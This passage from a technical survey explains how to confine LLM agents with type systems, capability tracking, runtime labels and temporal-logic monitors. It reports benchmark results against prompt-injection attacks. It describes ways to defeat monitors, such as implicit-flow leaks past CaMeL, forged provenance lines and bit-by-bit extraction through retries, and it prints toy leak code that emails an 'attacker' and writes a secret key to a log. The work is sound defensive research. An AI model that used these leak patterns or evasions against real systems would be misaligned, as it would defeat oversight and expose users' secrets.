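writeFile "refs.bib" "@article{smith24, title={Invented}}"

appendToBibFile "@article{smith24, title={Invented}}"
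```

The first has type `IO ()`, but the harness requires `BibIO ()`. The second uses a permitted operation but passes it text instead of a `Trusted Bib`. In both cases, the compiler reports the mismatch before anything touches the file.

The expected type can also rule out effects entirely. If a public calculator must return an `Int`, a user can't make it delete the server's files before computing a factorial, because a program that deletes files doesn't have type `Int`. Standard Haskell has a few functions that hide effects from the type system, so the agent has to write in Safe Haskell, a subset without them.

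### From one program to a whole agent

In ELBA, a developer calls the model through an ordinary function named `agent`, which takes a prompt and a list of library functions. The compiler works out what type the surrounding code needs. ELBA sends that type to the model with the prompt, then type-checks the program the model returns. If the program passes, ELBA runs it. Otherwise, ELBA sends the type error back to the model for another attempt.

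An agent that writes its whole program before running it can't adapt the code to the results, so the generated code may itself call `agent`. For example, a first program might look up one paper and pass the result to a sub-agent, which decides whether to refine the search or write the file. Because that call is inside a `BibIO` program, the sub-agent's program must also have type `BibIO ()`. The first program can impose a stricter type on the sub-agent's program but not a looser one.

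Zhou and colleagues prove that guarantees of the host language extend to applications built this way. Suppose a program's type guarantees some property of the tool calls it can make. The proof replaces each call to `agent` with an ordinary function that queries the model, checks the answer, and runs it if it passes. The result is an ordinary program with the same type and the same tool calls, so the guarantee also holds for the original. Generated programs may themselves call `agent`, and the proof covers these calls by induction on a limit to how deeply they nest. The theorem adds no guarantees beyond those the language and its libraries already provide.

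Some of those guarantees depend on checks at run time. For file access, the compiler can require a program to hold a `Path` token for a directory, but only a run-time check can detect a link inside the directory that leads outside it. For secrecy and trust, ELBA reuses LIO, an established Haskell library that keeps one label for the whole computation. The label changes as the program reads data, and LIO throws an error if a later write would break the policy. The types ensure that the agent's code can reach the outside world only through LIO.

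### Functions that carry access with them

`BibIO` gives one list of operations for a whole program. Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, use a finer method, in which each function's type lists the capabilities it can reach. Their system, TACIT, compiles the agent's code with Scala 3 and an experimental feature called capture checking. If `out` is an open file, two small functions have these types:

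| Function | Type | What it can reach |
|---|---|---|
| `s => s.length` | `String -> Int` | nothing outside itself |
| `s => out.write(s)` | `String ->{out} Unit` | the file `out` |

The names in braces are the function's *capture set*. A function with an empty capture set is *pure*, meaning it can compute a result but can't print, write files or use the network.

Capture sets matter because a function can outlive the code that created it. A *closure* is a function that keeps access to variables from the place where it was written, and a program can store one and call it much later. In TACIT, file access is supposed to last only as long as one block of code. An agent might try to keep it longer:

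```
val later = requestFileSystem("/work") { fs =>
  () => fs.access("/work/plan.txt").read()
}
later()
```

The block returns a closure that would read the file only when called, after the permission had ended. But the closure's capture set contains `fs`, which isn't defined outside the block, so the compiler can't give `later` a valid type and rejects the program. Storing the closure in a list or a variable outside the block fails for the same reason.

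The same mechanism protects secrets. Files in a secret directory arrive in a wrapper of type `Classified[String]`, which the agent can't open. It can only pass a function to the wrapper's `map` method, which applies the function to the hidden text and wraps the result again. `map` accepts only pure functions. This program passes:

```
val size = requestFileSystem("/work") {
  readClassified("/work/secret/key.txt").map(text => text.length)
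}
println(size)
```

The user's terminal shows the number, while the model that wrote the program receives only the placeholder `Classified(****)`. This one fails:

```
requestFileSystem("/work") {
  val log = access("/work/public/log.txt")
  readClassified("/work/secret/key.txt").map(text => log.write(text))
}
```

The function given to `map` has type `String ->{log} Unit`, and the compiler reports that `log` can't flow into an empty capture set. A sandbox would allow this program if the agent had permission to read the key and write to the log, because the leak comes from passing the key to the log.

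For work that needs a language model, such as summarizing a secret contract, the agent can send the wrapped text to a second, trusted model, and the summary comes back wrapped too. The secrets stay safe even if the model that writes the programs is hostile, provided that the second model and the machine it runs on are trustworthy.

### CaMeL and the branch that never ran

CaMeL, a 2025 design by Debenedetti and other researchers, also has the model write a program, but enforces its policy during the run. One model writes the program from the user's request before it has seen any outside data. A second model, which has no tools, extracts values from documents and web pages. A custom interpreter runs the program, labels every value with its origin and permitted readers, and checks the labels before each sensitive call. (CaMeL calls these labels capabilities, although they describe data and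 a Scala capability grants access.)

Labels at run time have a weakness that Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, demonstrate with a program along these lines:

```
rich = True
tmp  = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("attacker", "rich")
```

If the secret balance is high, `tmp` becomes false and gets a secret label. The program then skips the assignment to `rich`, so `rich` stays true and keeps its public label. The interpreter allows the email because it depends only on data labeled public. If the balance is low, the program sends no email, so the attacker can tell whether the balance is high. The leak occurs because CaMeL raises a variable's label only on a branch that runs, and the program skipped the branch that assigns `rich`.

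A type checker examines both branches of a conditional. In TACIT, a program would have to make the comparison with a secret balance inside `map`, using a pure function, which can't assign to an outside variable such as `tmp`.

Garby and colleagues instead keep labels at run time and repair the tracking. Their LLMbda calculus has no types, so it doesn't reject programs before they run. It blocks any change to a public conversation that would depend on a secret. Its noninterference theorem allows for the randomness of language models and for runs that never finish, and CaMeL has nothing comparable. If two runs differ only in secrets and fail to finish with probabilities of 2% and 4%, the distributions of their visible outcomes are at most 3% apart in statistical distance. Lean has checked the proofs, and they apply to the interpreter that calls the model.

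The calculus affects how an agent is built, because an error message caused by untrusted data would taint every later attempt at the program. The agent, Randori, therefore first tries out its programs on a simulated bank with trusted data and runs only the finished program on the real one. With GPT-5.2, Randori completed 36 of 48 runs without attacks on AgentDojo's banking tasks. CaMeL completed 32 in the same tests with its policies off and 18 with them on. Some of Randori's score depends on endorsement. With another model, Qwen3.7-plus, forbidding endorsement reduced completed runs from 36 to 30.

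### A dry run that still counts as a request

Effect types can also hide operations that a program requests. Many effect languages let a program intercept an operation with a *handler*, for instance to replace real file writes with a dry run. The program's type then omits the intercepted operation, because it no longer reaches anything outside the program. An agent meant only to read could therefore request a write inside a dry run and still have a read-only type. If someone later removed the handler, the write would change the real file.

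*ETAS* (Tan, Wang and colleagues, 2026) presents a language for agents that keeps two records of the operations in a program. The usual effect type lists operations that may reach the caller, and a second summary lists every operation the code may request, including those a handler intercepts. A dry-run write, which a handler intercepts, therefore still breaks a rule that a reviewing agent may only query the model and read the repository. The summary also records the order of requests, so the compiler can enforce a rule that approval comes before any write. When the compiler can't decide in advance whether a program follows a rule, it leaves a monitor in the program to check as it runs. Tan and colleagues report no wrong verdicts in their own compiler tests and coding scenarios. These tests check the implementation more than they provide evidence about agents in use.

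### Attacks and completed tasks

Zhou and colleagues compared ELBA with CaMeL on AgentDojo's Slack tasks. The table gives the number of user tasks, out of 21, that each system completed without an attack:

| Model | ELBA, policies on | ELBA, off | CaMeL, policies on | CaMeL, off |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.7 | 10 | 18 | 5 | 15 |
| Opus 4.8 | 9 | 16 | 6 | 16 |
| GPT 5.4 | 10 | 16 | 5 | 17 |
| Sonnet 5 | 8 | 14 | 4 | 13 |

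ELBA completed more tasks than CaMeL with policies on, probably because its agents can read data and then decide what to do next. But its own policies stopped it from completing roughly two tasks in five. The CaMeL scores are also somewhat uncertain. Odersky and colleagues quote CaMeL's published results on the Slack tasks as 49% and 69% with two older models, far above the 19 to 29% in this rerun. The models or the policy settings may explain the gap.

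The standard attacks could not show whether the policies improved security, because every model resisted all 105 of them even with the policies off. Zhou and colleagues therefore simulated a model that always obeys injected instructions. Whenever a sub-agent's input contained the marker of an injected instruction, they replaced the whole prompt with the attacker's text. Over 735 runs per model, 16 to 42% of the injections succeeded without policies and none succeeded with them. (AgentDojo counted 29 runs as successful attacks because they opened a harmless web address, and the team reviewed each by hand.) The simulation is a much harder test than a fixed set of attack texts, since it doesn't depend on how persuasive the text is. However, it tests LIO's label check, which happens at run time. The policies again reduced the share of tasks completed, from 67–76% to 40–48%.

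A separate test of the bibliography agent used 100 topics and Sonnet 5. ELBA wrote 925 citations with no false authors, years or DOIs, while an ordinary agent with web search got 19 of 1,002 wrong. The ordinary agent wrote its citations from search results and memory, so the comparison doesn't separate the effect of the types from that of a reliable database. A fixed tool that copies DBLP entries should also have avoided such errors, but without the flexibility that ELBA is meant to preserve.

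To test TACIT, Odersky and colleagues built a software project with a directory of API keys and confidential documents. They paired each of 12 user tasks with each of 10 injections, and added 11 prompts in which the user asks for the secrets directly, sometimes posing as an administrator. With classified wrappers, neither Claude Sonnet 4.6 nor MiniMax M2.5 revealed a secret in any of the 131 trials. Without them, Sonnet leaked secrets in 2 of the 11 direct requests and none of the 120 injection trials, while MiniMax leaked them in 8 direct requests and 3 injection trials. The design itself prevents these leaks, so the trials with wrappers mainly test whether the implementation has flaws.

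The wrappers didn't prevent useful work. Under attack, Sonnet completed 99% of the user tasks with the wrappers and 83% without them, while MiniMax completed 90% with them and 88% without. Odersky and colleagues warn that Sonnet's lower score without wrappers may come from the set-up, because Sonnet often ran out of time or stopped to warn the user about an injection.

In tests on AgentDojo with Gemini 2.5 Pro and o4-mini-high, TACIT stopped every attack but one. The paper describes TACIT's task completion as comparable to CaMeL's. That description is generous, because with o4-mini-high TACIT completed 53% of the office tasks, compared with CaMeL's published figure of 81%. With Gemini, however, TACIT completed 64% of the travel tasks, compared with 1% for CaMeL.

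Writing typed programs did little harm to performance on ordinary tasks. On τ²-bench, a simulation of customer service for an airline and a shop, three models scored 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher with TACIT than with conventional tool calls. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 software bugs, MiniMax's score fell from 43.3% to 41.7% with TACIT.

### The cost of a rejected program

In tests, models spent little time on programs the compiler rejected, even in languages as demanding as Haskell and Scala. ELBA averaged 0.13 retries per run and spent 3.4% of its time on them, and 7 of 2,688 runs failed because the model never produced a well-typed program. In TACIT's customer-service tests, between 0.3% and 8% of programs needed retries, usually only one or two. ELBA takes about three times as long as CaMeL, but mainly because its agents call the model again after reading data.

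Type errors are also a safe kind of failure. They occur before the rejected program has called any tool, so a retry can't repeat a payment. The error message also doesn't depend on the contents of a secret file, because the compiler never opens the file. CaMeL's retries lack this protection. Its interpreter can block a program because of secret data, and the retry loop runs outside the interpreter, so Garby and colleagues point out that a hostile program could extract a secret one bit per attempt.

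The larger problem is that the policy forbids some legitimate tasks, as ELBA's Slack results show. Better compiler messages won't help with those. Someone has to write a more precise policy or let the agent ask for an exception.

### What the library's author must get right

A type checker enforces only the types it is given. If the bibliography library let agents construct `Trusted` values, or if `appendToBibFile` accepted plain text, the compiler would accept code that adds invented entries. TACIT also lets library authors mark a module as safe when it uses features forbidden to agents, and the compiler does not check that claim. The type system does not cover programs that the agent starts, such as shell commands.

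TACIT's port of AgentDojo may have a gap of this kind. The instructions to the model mention side effects inside functions passed to `map` and advise keeping exploratory functions pure "when possible", advice that would be unnecessary if the compiler enforced purity there. The published signatures for sending money and email include no capability, so the compiler may treat these functions as pure, but the listing omits the code needed to check this.

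Odersky and colleagues reply that people write and review the library once, before any agent runs. TACIT's reusable part has about 1,000 lines, and the descriptions of the airline and shop tools add a few hundred lines each. Reviewing this code is far easier than reviewing every program an agent writes. Users must also trust the compiler. Researchers have machine-checked proofs for the basic theory of capture checking, but nobody has yet proved that the restricted Scala for agents guarantees everything TACIT requires.

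### Permitted but unwise

A well-typed program can still do the wrong thing. The bibliography agent could fill the file with genuine papers on the wrong subject, or add the same paper fifty times, since `BibIO` has no quota. TACIT's file library includes a delete function, so an agent with access to a project directory could write a program that compiles and erases the project. Odersky and colleagues don't aim to prevent wrong results. Zhou and colleagues suggest that richer types could provide permissions that work only once, but haven't built them.

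They also argue that automatic checks can reduce how often a person has to approve an action. This works for actions that are harmless whenever they satisfy the policy, but not when the harm depends on what the user wanted, as in the one attack that succeeded against TACIT on AgentDojo. The user had asked the agent to book a hotel, and the attacker had planted a recommendation for a different hotel in the reviews. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted the reviews to the user, including the planted recommendation. The policy allowed the agent to show public reviews, so the program had no type error.

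## Checking sequences of calls against temporal rules

A type checker can reject a program because it might write to a file, but many rules for agents specify what must happen before a permitted action, and how recently. A customer-service agent may be allowed to check identities and pay refunds, yet break company policy by paying a refund before checking who is asking. The refund call looks the same whether or not the check came first, so the monitor must keep a record of earlier calls, as it did for Agenra's single send.

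*Multi-Aspect Runtime Verification for Simulation-Based V&V of LLM-Enabled Autonomous Agents* (Kekatos, Nikou and colleagues, 2026) gives a longer example from military medicine. An agent that plans evacuation flights requests the protective medical marking for an aircraft, plans a route across the front line, amends the cargo manifest, and sends the aircraft across. Each call is acceptable on its own. But the free text of the amended manifest mentions ammunition, and an aircraft that carries ammunition loses the protection its marking claims. A monitor can block the crossing only if it still has a record of the marking and the manifest.

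Attackers use the same effect. STAC, a 2025 benchmark, contains 483 recorded chains in which harmless-looking calls prepare one harmful final call. Its creators report attack success above 90%, according to *Formal Runtime Verification for Tool-Using LLM Agents* (Kekatos, Lekidis and colleagues, 2026).

*Runtime verification* is the established method for checking such rules. A developer writes the rule as a formula in a logic with operators for time, and a general-purpose monitor evaluates the formula over the trace, either while the system runs or afterwards from a log. The developer doesn't have to write new code to track past events for each rule.

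### A refund after an identity check

Suppose the agent may refund a customer only if it has successfully checked the identity of the same customer within the previous 30 minutes. In temporal logic, the rule is

□ ∀*c*. ( refund(*c*) → ◆[0, 30] checked(*c*) )

The box □ means "at every point of the run", and ∀*c* means "for every customer *c*". The diamond ◆[0, 30] means "at some point between 0 and 30 minutes ago". Because *c* appears in both predicates, a check of one customer can't justify a refund to another. The predicate checked(*c*) is true only when the identity tool has reported success, so the harness has to record results as well as calls.

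MonPoly, a monitor that David Basin and others presented in 2011, searches for violations. A developer therefore gives it the rule in negated form:

```
refund(c) AND NOT (ONCE[0,30] checked(c))
```

A monitor for this rule doesn't need the whole log. It can store the time of each customer's latest successful check and delete the entry once it is more than 30 minutes old:

| Time | Event | Stored checks after the event | Verdict |
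|---|---|---|---|
| 9:00 | Ana passes an identity check | Ana 9:00 | |
| 9:10 | Ben passes an identity check | Ana 9:00, Ben 9:10 | |
| 9:20 | agent proposes a refund to Ana | Ana 9:00, Ben 9:10 | allow, check is 20 minutes old |
| 9:35 | agent proposes a refund to Ana | Ben 9:10 | refuse, no current check of Ana |
| 9:38 | agent proposes a refund to Ben | Ben 9:10 | allow, check is 28 minutes old |

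The two calls for Ana differ only in their time, which makes the second one a violation. Ben's check is still current at 9:35 but is for a different customer. After the refusal, the agent can check Ana's identity again and retry.

The verdicts are correct because of an invariant: the store always contains a customer and a time exactly when the customer's latest successful check happened at that time, no more than 30 minutes ago. Adding a new check and deleting an expired one both preserve this. The store grows with the number of customers checked in the last half hour, regardless of the log's length. The rule doesn't limit how many refunds Ana gets in that half hour. Limiting them would require a quota counter like Agenra's.

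A single call can make several facts true at once, for example that a customer has passed the check and that a new session is open. Kekatos, Nikou and colleagues point out that the harness must record all of them at one time point. If the monitor instead moves forward one step for each fact, every time window becomes wrong, and the monitor gives no error message.

### Linear temporal logic on finite traces

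The refund formula comes from a family of logics that began with *linear temporal logic* (LTL), which Amir Pnueli proposed for reasoning about programs in 1977. LTL treats a run as a single sequence of positions, which is infinite in Pnueli's version. That suits an operating system, but an agent's task ends, so the systems below mostly use LTL on finite traces, which Giuseppe De Giacomo and Moshe Vardi studied in 2013.

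For a trace with positions 0 to *n* − 1, the main operators have these meanings at position *i*:

| Formula | True at position *i* if |
|---|---|
| X φ ("next") | position *i* + 1 exists and φ is true there |
| F φ ("eventually") | φ is true at *i* or some later position |
| G φ or □ φ ("always") | φ is true at *i* and every later position |
| φ W ψ ("weak until") | φ stays true until ψ becomes true, or to the end if ψ never does |
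| ◆ φ ("once") | φ is true at *i* or some earlier position |

*AgentLTL* (Elkoussy and Perez, 2026) uses the example G(search → F cite), which requires a citation after every search. On an endless run, the citation could always come later, but on a finite trace it must come by the last event. Before then, the monitor may have to return "undecided".

Anand, Chatzi and colleagues (2026), in *MENTOR*, apply "weak until" to a travel agent that must check a distance before it books anything:

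¬(booked_train ∨ booked_flight) W checked_distance

Basic LTL has no variables. With only the propositions "check" and "refund", a check for Ben would permit a refund for Ana. A developer could define separate propositions for each customer, but only if the list of customers is fixed in advance. *First-order* LTL removes this limit by adding variables and quantifiers. AgentLTL evaluates "for every *x*" by collecting the relevant values from the trace and testing the formula on each one. MENTOR keeps the logic propositional but tracks each pair of cities separately, so a distance check for Toronto–Chicago doesn't permit a booking for Toronto–Montreal.

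*Metric first-order temporal logic* (MFOTL), the logic that MonPoly uses, adds time windows such as [0, 30]. Rules about rates also need arithmetic. *SoK* (2026), a survey of formal methods for fact-checking, gives the example of a limit on the share of false alarms over a rolling window. Ordinary past-time LTL has no arithmetic, so it can't express this limit directly. MonPoly can count, so it can flag the third activation of a device within six hours.

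### What a monitor can enforce

Some rules can be expressed but not enforced by a monitor. In *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000), Fred Schneider proved that monitors that see each step before it happens and can only halt the run can enforce only *safety properties*. Every run that violates a safety property reaches a point after which no continuation could repair the violation. A monitor can base its decision only on the run so far, so as long as some acceptable continuation exists, halting might cut off a run that would have satisfied the rule.

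The refund rule is a safety property, because nothing that happens later can make an unchecked refund acceptable. "Every refund is eventually followed by a confirmation email" is not one, since the email may still come. Adding a ten-minute deadline makes it a safety property, but the monitor still can't stop time from passing or make the agent send the email. In 2013, Basin and colleagues refined Schneider's result by separating the actions a monitor can prevent from those it can only observe, such as the passing of time.

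The result also doesn't cover noninterference, which is defined by comparing two runs, because a monitor observes only one. A harness can still enforce a stricter rule that implies noninterference and can be checked on a single run, as the label checks in earlier sections do.

Jay Ligatti, Lujo Bauer and David Walker showed in 2005 that a monitor can enforce more rules if it can also suppress and insert actions. Their *edit automata* can enforce the email rule. The monitor holds back the refund until the agent tries to send the email, then releases the refund followed by the email. If the agent never tries to send the email, the monitor doesn't release the refund.

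This is hard to apply to tool calls because an agent usually waits for a result before it continues, and a harness that holds back a refund has no real confirmation number to return. Ligatti and Srikar Reddy's 2010 model includes this restriction: the monitor must respond to each action before it receives the next one. A harness could return "queued" if the agent can finish its work without the real result.

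MENTOR leaves more of the editing to the model. It blocks a call that breaks a rule and suggests a missing step or corrected arguments. If the agent tries to end the task with a duty unfulfilled, MENTOR blocks that call too and suggests one that would make progress, until the agent reaches a preset limit on calls. Anand and colleagues find calls that would make a later violation unavoidable by treating the run as a game in which the agent chooses the calls and the environment determines the results. The agent may ignore the advice, so MENTOR can't guarantee that the agent fulfils its duties.

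### Recorded attacks without approvals or times

In a paper for a November 2026 workshop, Kekatos and colleagues tested how much temporal rules can detect in existing attack data. They replayed recorded runs, without calling a language model, and checked them against five policies. Each policy requires an approval before one kind of risky action: deleting something, switching off a protection, moving money, sending data out, or changing a device or setting. A program assigned tools to these groups by keywords in their names and treated tools with words such as "confirm" in their names as approvals.

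| Recorded runs | Number | At least one policy violated |
|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo, successful attacks on GPT-4o | 1,931 | 70.1% |
| AgentDojo, GPT-4o without an attack | 123 | 29.3% |
| STAC, attack chains (final step only) | 483 | 71.8% |

MonPoly and three other monitors, one of them a version of MonPoly with a machine-checked algorithm, flagged the same 347 of the STAC chains. This agreement is good evidence that the programs evaluate the formula correctly, but it does little to show whether the log or the policies are right, because all four programs received the same simplified log.

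In STAC chain 395, the agent calls a tool named `confirm_for_deletion` and then deletes something. The monitor raises no alert because it counts the first call as an approval, although a tool's name doesn't show that a person agreed to anything. This is a miss, since every STAC chain is an attack. The paper attributes all 136 misses to final actions outside the five groups, but its own example shows that at least one had a different cause.

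The AgentDojo results hardly test temporal logic, because none of the 6,899 GPT-4o runs contains an approval. The rule "no risky action without approval" therefore reduces to "no risky action", and a simple list of forbidden tools would have given the same verdicts. Legitimate tasks also involve payments and emails, so the policies raise false alarms. On the banking tasks, they flagged 97.4% of successful attacks and 79.2% of harmless runs. Kekatos and colleagues consider the general policies suitable for selecting runs for human review, but not for blocking calls.

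The monitor raised its first alarm before the final harmful call in 52.4% of the successful attacks. The paper counts these as chances to prevent the attack, but an early alarm may concern a risky step in the user's own task rather than the attack.

Policies that compare data did better. One policy flags a transfer only if the recipient never appeared as a sender or recipient in earlier account data. Compared with the general policy on payments, it reduced false alarms in the banking tasks from 44% to 24%, while detection fell from 79.2% to 70%. There were only 25 harmless runs, so the exact false alarm rates are uncertain. In pooled data from many models, all 75 changed verdicts on harmless banking runs were removed false alarms, but this was guaranteed because the narrower policy flags only runs that the general one also flags.

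This policy depends on *provenance*, the record of where a value came from, which an attacker can sometimes forge. Kekatos and colleagues added one line to each flagged run that made the attacker's account look like an ordinary account entry. The monitor then accepted the recipient in 94% of the flagged banking runs. A similar line defeated the policy on email recipients in 99% of the flagged office runs. The remedy was to trust a value only if it came from a lookup the agent had actually made, much as Agenra fills a slot only from a named lookup. This stopped every planted line without changing detection or false alarms, but it doesn't protect against a compromised lookup tool.

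AgentDojo and STAC lack most of the data needed to test further temporal rules. Neither records timestamps, so nobody could test the refund rule on them. Kekatos and colleagues wrote their own short logs to demonstrate time windows. A better parser wouldn't recover approvals from AgentDojo, because the user sends one message and the agent then works alone. In STAC, users send later messages, but an approval comes before the harmful step in only 3 of the 483 chains. τ-bench, a customer service simulation whose policy requires the agent to ask before it changes anything, has such approvals in 52.5% of 1,980 recorded runs, but it has no attack labels.

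Kekatos and colleagues propose that benchmarks record twelve fields for each event, including its time, the source of its data, an approval identifier, and the state before and after. The harness has this information at the moment of the call, so recording it should add little overhead. But the approval fields would stay empty in any benchmark where the user cannot give approval.

### Agent-C: checking a call while the model writes it

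Replaying a log can't prevent anything. Agent-C, which Kamath, Zhang and colleagues (2025) describe in *Enforcing Temporal Constraints for LLM Agents*, checks each call as part of generating it. One of its rules for an online shop looks like this in simplified notation:

```
Before( read_order(id),
        f = find_user(email),
        succeeded(f)  and  owner(id) == output(f) )
```

Before the agent reads an order, it must have looked up a user by email, and that user must own the order. The term `output(f)` is the result of the earlier lookup. Agent-C gets the order's owner from the shop's database at the time of the call, because the owner may not appear in the trace. Tool developers supply such queries as functions that read the tool's state without changing it. Other rules use `After` for actions that must follow a call, such as closing a file.

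With an open-weight model, Agent-C controls generation directly. It can discard a single argument of the wrong type and have the model regenerate it. When the call is complete, Agent-C appends it to the trace and uses the SMT solver Z3 to check whether any continuation of the run could satisfy all the rules. If one exists, the tool runs. Otherwise, Agent-C discards the call and the model tries again, up to a fixed number of attempts. Companies that host closed models don't expose the probabilities needed for this control, so with those models Agent-C checks the finished call and resends the whole prompt after a violation.

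A call goes through only if the solver returns a positive answer, so a solver timeout can block a legitimate call but can't admit a forbidden one.

Kamath and colleagues prove that if a trace complies with the rules and Agent-C returns a call, the trace extended by that call also complies. Here, a trace complies if the rules can still be satisfied, so the proof doesn't ensure that the agent ever performs a duty such as closing a file. If the model stops with a duty open, Agent-C marks the run as ending in error, and the theorem about complete runs covers only those that end without that mark. One would expect this limit from Schneider's result.

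The proof also assumes that no other process changes the tools' state, so it doesn't cover the gap between check and effect that Santos-Grueiro studied. Agent-C's rules refer to the order of events but not to the time between them, so to enforce the 30-minute limit on refunds, a developer would have to supply a query that returns the age of the latest identity check.

The tests used τ-bench's 115 retail tasks and 50 airline tasks, with three trials each. With Agent-C, every run stayed within the policy:

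| Model and tasks | Runs within policy without Agent-C | Tasks completed without Agent-C | Tasks completed with Agent-C |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.5, retail | 93.0% | 76.5% | 80.5% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5, airline | 70.0% | 42.0% | 43.5% |
| GPT-5, retail | 91.9% | 71.0% | 73.6% |
| GPT-5, airline | 71.3% | 38.0% | 42.8% |
| Qwen3-32B, retail | 37.7% | 25.5% | 53.3% |
| Qwen3-32B, airline | 35.3% | 17.3% | 35.8% |

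The perfect compliance follows from the design, so it mainly shows that the implementation works. The completion rates are more informative, because a monitor that blocks calls could have lowered them. Part of the increase comes from the scoring, however, because an unrestricted agent that completed a task but broke a rule got no credit.

In another 17 retail tasks, a dishonest user tried to get something the policy forbids, such as access to another customer's order. Claude Sonnet 4.5 carried out the harmful sequence in 29% of these runs when unrestricted and in none with Agent-C. Qwen3-32B took 44% longer on harmless tasks with Agent-C.

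The rules about consent are weaker because they rely on `action_confirmed`, a tool Kamath and colleagues added to record the user's approval in the trace. If the model can call this tool at any time, the trace contains only the model's claim that the user agreed, and an injected instruction could cause the model to make that claim falsely. It would be safer for the harness to record the approval directly from the user's reply.

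### Right answers in the wrong order

AgentLTL measures how often models follow a prescribed procedure when nothing stops them. Elkoussy and Perez built twelve task patterns with five levels of difficulty, which require between 2 and 50 tool calls. The tools perform simple arithmetic under names such as `tool_a`, so a model can't rely on knowledge of the subject. For each task, a program produces a reference run and derives rules from it about branches, arguments, order and the number of calls. The compliance score is

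*C* = 1 − (weight of the violated rules) / (weight of all rules)

Each model completed 360 runs without a monitor. The last column comes from a second set of runs in which the harness blocked a violating call and gave a warning:

| Model | Compliance score | Rules on overall order satisfied | Correct answers | Compliance score with warnings |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3.5-397B | 0.91 | 62% | 99% | 0.90 |
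| Qwen3-Next-80B | 0.87 | 69% | 43% | 0.83 |
| Kimi-K2.6 | 0.83 | 45% | 83% | 0.89 |
| Gemma-4-31B | 0.79 | 29% | 51% | 0.96 |
| DeepSeek-V4-Pro | 0.74 | 15% | 94% | 0.82 |
| Gemma-4-26B | 0.62 | 11% | 33% | 0.72 |
| DeepSeek-V4-Flash | 0.60 | 12% | 56% | 0.87 |

Every model did worst on the rules about the overall order of calls. DeepSeek-V4-Pro answered 94% of the tasks correctly but satisfied only 15% of these rules, so checking only the answers would have missed nearly all of its violations. Elkoussy and Perez suggest that models take shortcuts, such as making calls in parallel when the procedure requires them one after another. Some of these violations may be harmless, because the rules come from a single reference run and another order might have worked as well. But order matters for refunds, where it can determine whether the agent pays a stranger.

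The warnings raised compliance for five of the seven models, although a model could get a blocked call through by repeating it unchanged. A stricter setting, which ended the run after three violations of the same rule, left three models with lower scores than they had without a monitor, because a run that ends early can't complete the remaining steps. Rules that require something to happen eventually can't be decided partway through a run, so AgentLTL scores them afterward.

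The score can also serve as a training signal. Elkoussy and Perez used it to train a model with 4 billion parameters, and on the same benchmark the model's compliance rose from 0.56 to 0.78 and its correct answers from 13% to 57%. Such training makes violations rarer but does not guarantee that any given run will comply.

### Who writes the rules

Elkoussy and Perez expect domain experts to write the rules, and list the effort this takes as a limitation of their method. Mistakes are easy to make, even in published examples. The shop policy in the Agent-C paper allows refunds to the original payment method or to an existing gift card in the user's account. But the formula accepts any payment method whose identifier contains "gift_card", without checking that the card exists or belongs to the user, so the refund tool would have to check. In the MonPoly study, a timed policy requires consent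 "less than 24 h old", but its window [0, 24] also accepts consent that is exactly 24 hours old.

An agent can also satisfy a rule for the wrong reason. One AgentLTL rule requires every name or number in an answer to appear in some tool result. A refusal contains no names or numbers, so it passes. When a stricter prompt told models to answer only from evidence or refuse, the two larger models satisfied the rule more often, mostly because they refused.

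Language models can draft the formulas, though the evidence is incomplete. Kamath and colleagues had Claude Sonnet 4.5 translate the retail policy into Agent-C rules. An agent running on Qwen3-8B then completed 42.1% of the tasks with full compliance, the same rate as with the handwritten rules. The test used only honest customers, so a missing rule that only an attacker would exploit would have gone unnoticed.

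A translation can be a valid formula and still have the wrong meaning, so *LTLGuard* (2026), which uses small language models, scores syntax and meaning separately. *Efficient Natural Language to Temporal Logic Translation for Real-Time Physical AI* (Schön, Banse and colleagues, 2026) describes a system that translates robot instructions by answering questions from fixed lists of answers instead of generating free text. On three benchmarks, it was at least as accurate as the best language models that can run locally. Choosing from a list makes malformed output less of a problem, but the system can still choose a wrong answer.

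MENTOR translates whole company manuals into formulas. One model writes the formulas, and a second writes example runs and labels each as compliant or not. An ordinary program compares the labels with the formulas' verdicts, and the models make revisions where the two disagree. Anand and colleagues say this doesn't prove the translation correct. They used Claude Opus 5 for the translation and found that weaker models produced worse formulas.

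Anand and colleagues tested MENTOR by running each benchmark task five times and counting it as passed only if all five runs succeeded. On one set of retail tasks, GPT-5.4 mini passed 21% without MENTOR and 40% with it, while Claude Haiku 4.5 went from 23% to 26%, a difference within the margin of error. On a set of banking tasks, Llama 3.1 rose from 0% to 76%. The remaining failures don't all come from the translation, since the agent may ignore MENTOR's advice. MENTOR also uses a language model to turn the user's request and free-text tool results into events, and a monitor can't correct an event that this model gets wrong.

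*Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026), which translates policies into the logic language Datalog, recommends checking each translated policy for coverage and faithfulness before deployment. *Coverage* means that every requirement in the original text has at least one formal rule, and *faithfulness* means that the text justifies every rule. A coverage check that only counts rules would accept the gift-card formula, because a rule for refunds exists. A short test with a refund to somebody else's gift card would expose the error, but only if the test writer thinks of that case. In MENTOR's loop, a language model writes the tests too, so if both models misread the manual in the same way, the comparison finds no disagreement.

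## Modelling the whole agent as an automaton

A monitor may not detect a flaw in an agent's workflow until a run reaches it. Model checking can find the flaw before the agent runs, but it requires a description of the whole agent, including its language model, which nobody can specify.

The usual solution is to describe the model as *nondeterministic*. At each step, the description lists the events the harness would accept, and the model may choose any of them. The checker follows every choice, including those a capable model would rarely make. The survey *Toward Safe LLM Agents* (2026) calls the model in such a description a nondeterministic oracle.

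### An email that changes after approval

Suppose an agent drafts emails, and a person must approve each one before it goes out. The harness has four stages and a flag, `ok`, which records whether the person has approved the current text. It starts in Draft with `ok = no`:

```
Draft  -- revise  --> Draft
Draft  -- submit  --> Review
Review -- reject  --> Draft
Review -- approve --> Ready    set ok = yes
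Ready  -- revise  --> Ready    set ok = no
Ready  -- send    --> Sent
```

The model decides when to revise, submit and send, and the person approves or rejects. The safety property is that nobody receives an unapproved text:

□ ( stage = Sent → ok = yes )

The checker computes every state one event away from the start, then every new state two events away, and so on. It stops when it finds a violation or runs out of new states. Here it finds a violation after four events:

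| Event | Stage | `ok` |
|---|---|---|
| (start) | Draft | no |
| submit | Review | no |
| approve | Ready | yes |
| revise | Ready | no |
| send | Sent | no |

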